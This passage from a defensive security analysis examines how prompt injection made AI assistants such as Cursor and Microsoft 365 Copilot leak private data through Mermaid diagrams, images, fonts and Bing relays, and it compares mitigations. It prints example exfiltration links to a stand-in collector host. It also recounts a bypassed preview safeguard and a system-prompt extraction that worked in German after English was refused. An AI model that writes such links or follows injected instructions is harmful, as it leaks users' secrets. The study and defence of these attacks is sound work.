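Cursor probably blocked ordinary images, but the evidence is indirect. On Embrace The Red, Rehberger calls images inside Mermaid diagrams "a new variant" but doesn't say whether an ordinary image would have leaked the same data. He had reported Windsurf's ordinary image leak a month earlier, so he would probably have tried an ordinary image in Cursor and reported it if it had worked. GitHub's two records of the Cursor flaws also mention only diagrams. Someone would need to test a version of Cursor older than 1.3 to be sure.

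### Blocking a notation or blocking a request

A filter that looks for Markdown links will not necessarily recognise a Mermaid link, even when both lead to the same address:

```
[Log in](https://collector.example/r?d=626c7565)
click A href "https://collector.example/r?d=626c7565"
```

Microsoft hasn't published its filter, so this explanation of why Logue's link got through is an inference. But the filter had already missed a less common form of Markdown in EchoLeak, and Mermaid's notation differs even more from ordinary Markdown.

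Microsoft made a similar mistake with another feature soon afterwards. In September or October 2025, Rehberger noticed that Copilot could display a small web page inside the chat. Copilot removed image tags from the page, so he asked it to write one that loaded outside material in as many ways as possible. A style rule with a background picture worked. The content security policy limited where that picture could come from, but it restricted fonts less, and a font request carried the text of an email to his server. Rehberger reported the first version of this attack on 16 October, twenty days after Microsoft fixed the diagram leak. Microsoft finished fixing it in March 2026.

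The second Cursor flaw supports the same conclusion, since the bypasses listed in the NVD suggest that Anysphere had blocked some forms of diagram image but not others.

The main evidence against this explanation is that vendors didn't rely only on recognizing notation. A content security policy applies to an image request whether the image came from Markdown, HTML or a diagram, which may be why Copilot's diagrams didn't load outside images. But the policy's list of allowed image servers doesn't restrict where links lead, so Microsoft relied on finding links in the text. Its claim to cover variants may have been true of images in diagrams but not of links.

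Rehberger's image came from his own server, so Cursor's chat window either had no policy on images or had one loose enough to allow it. If Cursor did block ordinary images, it must have done so in its Markdown code or with some other check that diagrams bypassed.

Someone could settle much of this by giving an old version of Cursor the same external image in Markdown and in a diagram, then checking whether each one triggers a request. Only Microsoft can run the equivalent test on Copilot as it was in August 2025, because Copilot runs on Microsoft's servers.

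### Protection against scripts

Mermaid's developers built most of its protections to stop scripts, not to stop diagrams from loading images from other servers. This was reasonable for an ordinary website, because an image URL that a stranger puts in a diagram contains only what the stranger already knows. The URL becomes dangerous when a language model with access to private data can fill in part of it, because loading the image then sends that data to the server.

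A developer who read that Mermaid's default was "strict" could easily have assumed that this setting was safe for diagrams written by a model. But no statement from Anysphere or Microsoft shows that their developers assumed this.

Mermaid's maintainers also knew that diagrams could trigger outside requests. GitHub Security Lab had described in 2022 how CSS in a diagram could leak data through background images. Mermaid's strict security level should have stopped the label Rehberger used, unless its sanitization failed. If Cursor used a looser level, Anysphere had turned off a protection that Mermaid offered.

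Cursor's Mermaid version and security level in June 2025 would show how much Mermaid's design contributed to the Cursor leak. If Cursor used the "strict" level, the design explains a good deal of it. The design explains less of the Copilot leak, because images didn't load there and Mermaid's documentation had always presented links as a feature developers should think about.

### Trust in the model's own text

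Developers may have checked what users typed but trusted the model's answers as their own application's text. LobeChat passed diagram text, including text from the model, to its renderer without cleaning it. A summary in Vulners' *GitHub* attributes one GitHub Copilot leak to "insecure output handling", OWASP's term for passing a model's output to other software without sufficient checks.

In summer 2025, the security company Zenity showed that a different attack could work against Cursor, in which a hostile support ticket made it steal an access token through a connected Jira account. In a reply quoted by Willison, Anysphere called this "a known issue" and advised users to connect only to services with trusted content. That advice is meant to keep hostile text away from the model, but it doesn't address what happens to the model's answer once hostile text has got in, and the diagram leak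 occurred at that stage.

Still, the reply was about connected services, and Anysphere did fix the diagram renderer when Rehberger reported the flaw. The explanation fits Microsoft poorly. In July 2025, the company wrote that some injections might get past its defences and that it designs its products so that these don't harm customers. It also filters links out of its assistant's answers, so it does not trust those answers.

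The term "insecure output handling" does little to show whether developers trusted the model's output. It describes a missing or failed check, and developers who distrusted the model could have written a check that failed. *EchoLeak*, for example, applies the term to the step in which Copilot wrote a link to the attacker's server, although Microsoft had a filter for such links. Design documents from before the reports would be better evidence, particularly if they listed the sources of untrusted text and left out the model.

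### New features and security reviews

Cursor added Mermaid diagrams to its chat in version 1.0. The release's changelog, *Bugbot, Background Agent access to everyone, and one-click MCP install*, says that diagrams and tables "can now be generated and viewed in the same place". An unofficial copy of the changelog, Cursor (2025), gives the date as 4 June 2025. Rehberger reported the leak 26 days later.

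The same release introduced memories, which Rehberger stole in one of his two demonstrations, and a quicker way to add MCP servers, which he named as a source of further data. Anysphere had thus given the assistant more private information and a new way to send it out. A reviewer who looked at memories and diagrams separately might have approved both, because the leak requires both private data and a diagram that loads a picture from an address containing that data.

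Microsoft fixed Visual Studio's built-in diagrams about a month after announcing them, a similarly short interval. Copilot's web page preview was also new when Rehberger found the leak in it.

These dates show only that the features were new, not that anyone skipped a review or that the companies had reviews a new feature could miss. A reviewer could have examined the diagrams in Cursor 1.0 and thought only about scripts. Anysphere's developers certainly examined them in July, when they were writing the first patch, but they still left several bypasses, which a lack of time before the release can't explain.

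It is unclear whether Microsoft added diagrams to Microsoft 365 Copilot before or after it began filtering links. The filter's developers may never have considered diagrams if they were added later, but overlooked an existing feature if diagrams came first. Internal release records could settle the order for both companies, and would also show whether anyone tested a diagram containing an outside address.

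### Bounties and severity scores

Some vendors gave researchers little reason to look for image leaks. OpenAI first responded to the problem with "won't fix". In November 2025, a researcher reported an ordinary Markdown image leak in Antigravity, Google's AI code editor, and said Google had classed it as intended behaviour. Google also listed data exfiltration through prompt injection as a known issue in Antigravity, so reports of it earned no reward. Willison describes both the report and the listing, and notes that Google said it was working on a fix. A few weeks earlier, Microsoft had refused Logue a bounty.

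But researchers were testing heavily in 2025. In August, Rehberger published a report every day on flaws in AI tools. The researcher behind CamoLeak scored it 9.6 and reported it through HackerOne, a service that runs bounty programmes. For the two diagram leaks, the discouraging news also came after the research was done. GitHub published its score of 4.4 for the first Cursor flaw, which MITRE records, a month after Rehberger's report. Logue learned that Copilot was outside the bounty's scope only after doing the work.

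A low score might instead have discouraged other vendors from checking their own renderers after August, although Microsoft gave the flaw the same 4.4 in Visual Studio and still fixed it.

Microsoft also paid Rehberger a bounty in December 2025 for the leak through Copilot's web page preview, two months after Logue published that he had been refused one. Either the rules had changed or Microsoft applied them differently. If the rules changed on a known date, comparing the number of Copilot reports before and after it would show whether the lack of bounties had deterred researchers. The comparison would not explain why the vendors' own testers, who don't depend on bounties, had missed the diagrams.

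## Which defences close the leak, and what do they leave open?

The most complete defence is to turn the diagram into a static picture on a machine with no internet access, because the picture then contains no working links, scripts or outside addresses. A vendor that wants interactive diagrams needs to combine several measures, because each leaves at least one route open when used alone: an isolated frame, a content security policy that allows no outside servers, and some control over links. In 2026, researchers reported two further leaks in Microsoft 365 Copilot that got past content security policies because the policies allowed too many servers.

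### Removing images or links from the diagram

An application can delete image tags from labels before it passes the text to Mermaid. This stops the kind of label Rehberger used against Cursor, and users lose only the pictures in their diagrams, such as logos. The deletion has to happen before Mermaid makes its temporary drawing, and it has to cover image nodes too. It does not stop leaks through links or style rules.

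Filters of this kind often miss something. Researchers got around both Cursor's first patch and DeepChat's attribute filter. A safer design allows a short list of parts, such as boxes, arrows and plain text, and discards everything else, including unfamiliar features. Some legitimate diagrams will then look wrong or fail to draw.

Disabling links, as Microsoft did in Copilot, closes the one-click route and also stops `javascript:` addresses like the one used against Dify. It doesn't stop images or fonts from loading automatically. Users can no longer click from a box to a document, but an application could keep links to its own pages, such as other notes in the same notebook, and remove only those that lead elsewhere.

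### A stricter level and a second sanitiser

Mermaid's strict level may still let image nodes and style rules load outside files, and users give up HTML formatting in labels.

Mermaid describes the setting as a level of trust and makes the site's owner responsible for distinguishing trustworthy users from untrustworthy ones. That advice fits a website where each user writes their own diagrams. In an AI assistant, a stranger's hidden instructions can produce a diagram in a trusted employee's chat, so the developer has to treat every diagram as untrusted.

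A second sanitiser checks the finished SVG before the application puts it on the page. The component library markstream-vue runs this check under both strict and loose Mermaid settings. Open WebUI didn't have one when it used the loose setting and inserted the SVG directly into the page.

How much of the leak the sanitiser stops depends on what its developers tell it to remove. For example, markstream-vue's rules for ordinary Markdown images block addresses that begin with two slashes, because these "can silently load external resources", but accept addresses that begin with `https:`, which also load external resources and can still leak data. A sanitiser for model output would have to remove every outside address, including those in style rules. Even then, it would run too late to stop a request that began during the temporary drawing.

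### Isolated frames at GitHub, GitLab and Visual Studio Code

GitHub's *Include diagrams in your Markdown files with Mermaid* (2022) describes how GitHub draws the Mermaid diagrams in users' documents inside iframes. While converting a document to HTML, GitHub replaces each code block marked as Mermaid with a template. If the reader's browser runs JavaScript, the page then adds an iframe that loads from Viewscreen, GitHub's internal service for displaying files. The iframe passes the raw diagram text to Mermaid, which draws the diagram in the reader's browser.

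GitHub chose the design partly for security. It says the frame gives users' text "less potential to cause mischief" on the surrounding page. The frame also keeps the Mermaid library out of the main page's code and lets the page appear without waiting for its diagrams.

GitLab, another code-hosting company, adopted a similar design to limit the damage from script flaws in Mermaid. According to GitLab's *Render GFM Mermaid diagrams in a sandboxed iframe*, the page sends the diagram text to the frame as a message, and the frame sends back the size of the drawing so the page can make room for it. The frame loads from the same GitLab server, but the sandbox setting makes the browser treat it as a different site. A script in the diagram therefore can't read the surrounding page or use the reader's login.

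Mermaid's own sandbox level turns scripts off inside the frame, so the library has to run in the main page. GitHub and GitLab instead run the library inside the frame. This confines the effects of any flaw in the library but requires them to allow scripts in the frame. An attacker's script might then run there and read the diagram text, which in an assistant's answer may already contain the secret.

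A frame alone also does not stop a zero-click leak, because a request for a remote image can still send out any data in the image's address.

In Visual Studio Code, Microsoft's code editor, extensions display custom content in webviews, which are similar to iframes. Webviews cannot directly read files on the user's computer, but they can load images from outside websites. *Webview API*, Visual Studio Code's guide for extension developers, builds an example webview that uses the default options and shows a picture from Giphy. An image address with an API key at the end would load in the same way.

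In May 2026, Microsoft built Mermaid into Visual Studio Code's Markdown preview, notebooks and chats (Visual Studio Code, 2026). The Markdown preview is a webview. The announcement doesn't give the Mermaid security level or the content security policy, so it's unclear from the announcement whether a diagram in a chat can load an outside image.

Frames also have drawbacks. Visual Studio Code's guide warns that webviews use a lot of resources, and Mermaid warns that its sandbox level may interfere with scripts, pop-ups in sequence diagrams, and links to other tabs.

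### Limiting where the browser can send requests

A strict content security policy for a frame that only draws diagrams could look like this:

```
default-src 'none';
script-src https://app.example/mermaid/;
style-src 'unsafe-inline';
img-src data:;
font-src data:
```

The first line blocks everything the later lines don't permit. The browser may load scripts only from the folder that holds Mermaid. It may apply styles written inside the drawing, which Mermaid needs for its colours. It may show images and fonts only if their data is already in the page. The policy therefore blocks outside images, whether they come from a tag, an image node or a background rule. It also blocks scripts attached to image tags.

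Visual Studio Code's guide recommends starting with the same first line, but its fuller example then allows images from any `https:` address. That is reasonable for an extension that displays pictures of cats, but it would be a poor choice for model output because it would leave the image route completely open.

Before version 11.15.0, a policy that blocked outside images but not outside fonts would have left a leak open. Diagram text could add CSS rules to the whole page, and OSV lists `@font-face` among them. This rule can make the browser download a font from an address the attacker chooses.

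A policy can also break diagrams. A GitLab user reported seeing a bomb icon and the words "Syntax error in text" in place of a diagram. The browser's log showed that the policy had blocked two scripts that Mermaid apparently needed. The error message would have led most people to look for a mistake in their diagram.

Content security policies don't normally stop a user from following a link to another site. In Copilot, a click replaced the diagram with the attacker's page. The page around a frame can list the sites that the frame may show, which should prevent this. A link that opens a new tab needs a separate control. Salesforce added one after researchers used an expired domain listed in its policy to extract customer data. According to Willison, the company corrected its policy and then introduced "Trusted URLs", which stops its agent from writing links to untrusted domains.

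An application can also send every outside request through a proxy, a server that fetches content on the user's behalf. A simple proxy hides the user's IP address from the attacker but passes on the rest of the request, including the secret. To close the leak, the proxy has to block requests to some web addresses.

Embrace The Red describes a check that Google and OpenAI use against these leaks. Their assistants can open an address without asking the user only if the company's search index already lists it as public. An address containing a newly stolen password won't be in the index, so the check blocks it. The check also stops the assistants from automatically opening new or private pages.

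An attacker could still spell out a secret through pages published in advance, much as Rehberger did with ChatGPT's earlier check. For a 40-character key made of lower-case letters and digits, the attacker could prepare 1,440 pages (40 × 36), one for each possible character in each position. The assistant would have to request 40 of them, whereas one request would be enough without the check. Rehberger accepts that the check isn't a complete fix but recommends it because it limits large thefts. He doubts that Microsoft's Copilots use anything similar yet.

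### SearchLeak and the trusted relay

*SearchLeak* (2026), published by the security company Varonis on 15 June, describes an attack of the same name on the search feature of Microsoft 365 Copilot. The attack began with a link to Microsoft's website. Copilot treated the search text in the link as instructions. It searched the victim's email, took the title of a message and put it into the address of an image.

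Microsoft had two defences against such an image. One was to wrap Copilot's answer in a code block, which makes the browser show an image tag as text. But Copilot added the wrapping only after it had finished writing, so while the answer was still appearing, the browser treated the tag as a real image and requested it.

The content security policy should then have blocked the request. It excluded the attacker's server but allowed all of Bing, Microsoft's search engine, which has a feature that fetches an image from any address included in a request. The browser requested the image from Bing, and Bing requested it from the attacker's server, which recorded the email's title. Services often put login codes in email titles, so the title alone may be enough for an attacker.

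Varonis calls this a one-click attack because the victim had to open the link. The image in Copilot's answer then leaked data without another click. The Next Web points out that filters for suspicious links were unlikely to catch an address on microsoft.com.

Either of Microsoft's defences could have stopped the leak if it had worked properly. Varonis recommends cleaning the output as it is displayed and checking every allowed domain for services that fetch user-supplied addresses. Both apply to diagrams, since Mermaid's final cleaning also comes late and a diagram could leak data through the same kind of service.

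Microsoft already knew from EchoLeak that an allowed server could relay data. Even a short list of allowed servers isn't necessarily safe. Bing Chat's 2023 policy allowed only Bing's own domains, and a Bing feature relayed the data in SearchLeak.

### CVE-2026-24299 and the preview that opened itself

In CVE-2026-24299, Copilot's web page preview leaked an email through a font request. In one of Rehberger's demonstrations, the victim only had to open a shared Word document containing hidden instructions and type "hi there" to Copilot.

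Rehberger found that Copilot's content security policy had a different list of allowed servers in the chat application than in SharePoint and Excel on the web. Some lists included `azureedge.net`, where Microsoft's customers could have their own addresses. Some entries contained what looked like employees' user names, which suggests that individual employees had added them. Rehberger concludes that the policy is not a reliable barrier in Copilot.

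His evidence supports that conclusion for Copilot but is a weaker argument against such policies in general. A policy that allowed no outside fonts would have blocked his request. The preview was vulnerable because it relied on whichever page it appeared in to set the rules. A diagram component that several products share would have the same weakness, which its developers could avoid by drawing diagrams in a frame with its own strict policy.

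Copilot also had a safeguard that displayed the page's code by default, so the browser loaded nothing until the user switched to the preview. Rehberger bypassed it by adding a line to his hidden instructions that asked Copilot to show the preview, which Copilot then opened without a click. Microsoft published the CVE record two weeks after it finished fixing the leak.

### Converting the diagram to a static picture

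When a browser displays an SVG file with an `<img>` tag, as it would a photograph, it doesn't run the file's scripts, follow its links or load outside resources. A PNG file stores only pixels, so it can't contain any of these. Converting a diagram to either form therefore closes all four routes in the user's window.

Converting the diagram to a picture can still leak the secret. Mermaid has to draw the diagram first, normally in a browser. If the vendor runs that browser on its own server, the browser may fetch the remote image, which would send the secret out from the vendor's server instead of the user's computer. Cutting off the converter's internet access prevents this.

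Users can no longer click on parts of the diagram. If it is a PNG, they also can't select its text, and it blurs when they zoom in. People who use screen readers need a separate description.

A renderer can also draw a static diagram with text characters, which can't request an image. Willison (2026), in *Mermaid to Unicode box art (grok-mermaid)*, examined one such renderer from the code of Grok CLI, a coding agent that runs in a terminal. His browser version handles five kinds of diagram, including flowcharts and sequence diagrams, and shows the source text of any other kind in a frame. He doesn't present the renderer as a security measure. Many terminals make printed web addresses clickable, so a one-click leak could remain if the renderer prints the address.

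### Asking before a link opens

An application can show the full address and ask for confirmation before it opens a link or loads an image. This turns a zero-click leak into a one-click leak, as Claude's "Show Image" button did in 2023. A careful user who clicks a disguised button can still cancel, but the confirmation interrupts the user each time.

Whether the user can make a good decision depends on what the application shows when it asks for confirmation. The hexadecimal in Logue's address would have looked like the meaningless codes in many legitimate links. The destination server's name is more useful, particularly if the application also mentions that the link came from an AI's answer and leads outside the company.

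The application itself has to ask for approval and accept an answer only from the user. Copilot's preview did not meet this requirement, because the model could open it. Users may also tire of these requests and approve them without reading them. Partly to reduce this "prompt fatigue", Microsoft offers an automatic mode for the Claude agent in Visual Studio Code, in which a classifier, rather than the user, reviews the agent's actions.

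### The defences compared

The table assumes that developers use each defence alone.

| Defence | Remote image | Clickable link | Remote CSS resource | Script | What users lose |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Removing images from labels | Closes tags; image nodes need separate handling | Open | Open | Stops only scripts attached to images | Pictures in diagrams |
| Disabling links | Open | Closed | Open | Stops only scripts in links | Navigation from the diagram |
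| Mermaid's strict level | Should close tags; no stated block on image nodes | Officially disabled, but some links may work | No stated block | Meant to close; has had flaws | HTML labels and clicks |
| Second sanitiser on the drawing | Closed only if it removes outside addresses; may run too late | Closed only if it removes links | Closed only if it checks styles; may run too late | Mostly closed | Whatever it removes |
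| Isolated frame | Open | Depends on the frame's settings | Open, but cannot style the page | Cannot read the page; may read the diagram | Speed and some interaction |
| Strict content security policy | Closed, except through allowed servers | Open | Closed if it covers fonts, images and style sheets | Blocks scripts it does not list | Outside images and fonts |
| Allowlist or checking proxy | Closed, except through relays | Closed if it checks links | Closed if it checks every request | Limits where a script can send data | Access to unlisted sites |
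| Static picture made offline | Closed | Closed | Closed | Closed | Clicks, and text selection in some formats |
| Confirmation | User decides, if it covers images | User decides | Open unless it covers these requests | Open | Time and attention |

### Training the model or blocking the request

A vendor can also train its model to ignore hidden instructions, or filter them out before the model reads them. If this works, the assistant never writes the secret into a diagram. Either defence can also prevent harm that needs no outside request. For example, a content security policy could not have stopped Rehberger from making Copilot store false memories about a user, including that the user was 102 years old and preferred answers in Mandarin Chinese.

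Attackers can still reword their instructions. Rehberger saw this when he asked Copilot to reveal its own settings. It had once refused to print its system prompt (the vendor's standing instructions to the model) in English but printed it in German. When he tried again in 2026, Copilot refused the German request and also refused to list its tools, but it wrote the tools' names into an XML document (a structured data format). Rehberger made these requests directly, not through hidden instructions, but they show that a model can refuse one wording and accept another.

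Model-side defences can still stop real attacks. Before his talk, Rehberger tried to repeat an attack on the consumer version of Copilot, but it now consistently blocked his document. Microsoft could no longer reproduce the attack either. Rehberger thinks the company had added filters, but he gives no success rates from before and after, so his test doesn't show how well Copilot would resist a new version of the document.

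Training that greatly reduces an attack's success rate could still leave many victims. At a rate of one in a thousand, for example, an attacker who got the same document in front of 10,000 users would succeed about ten times. A strict content security policy would block the image request every time.

Rehberger, like Willison, favours limiting outside communication. SearchLeak and the font attack show how vendors get this wrong too. But while a security team can't list every sentence that might mislead a model, it can list every server that a policy allows and test each one for relays.

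Blocking requests should therefore be the first defence against diagram leaks. Training should supplement it by making attacks rarer and limiting the harm that needs no request. Rehberger warns that users of more robust models tend to become careless and assume the model will enforce security. Developers could make the same mistake with Visual Studio Code's automatic mode. Its classifier reviews the agent's actions before they run, but a diagram can leak data when the application displays an answer, and displaying an answer may not count as an action.
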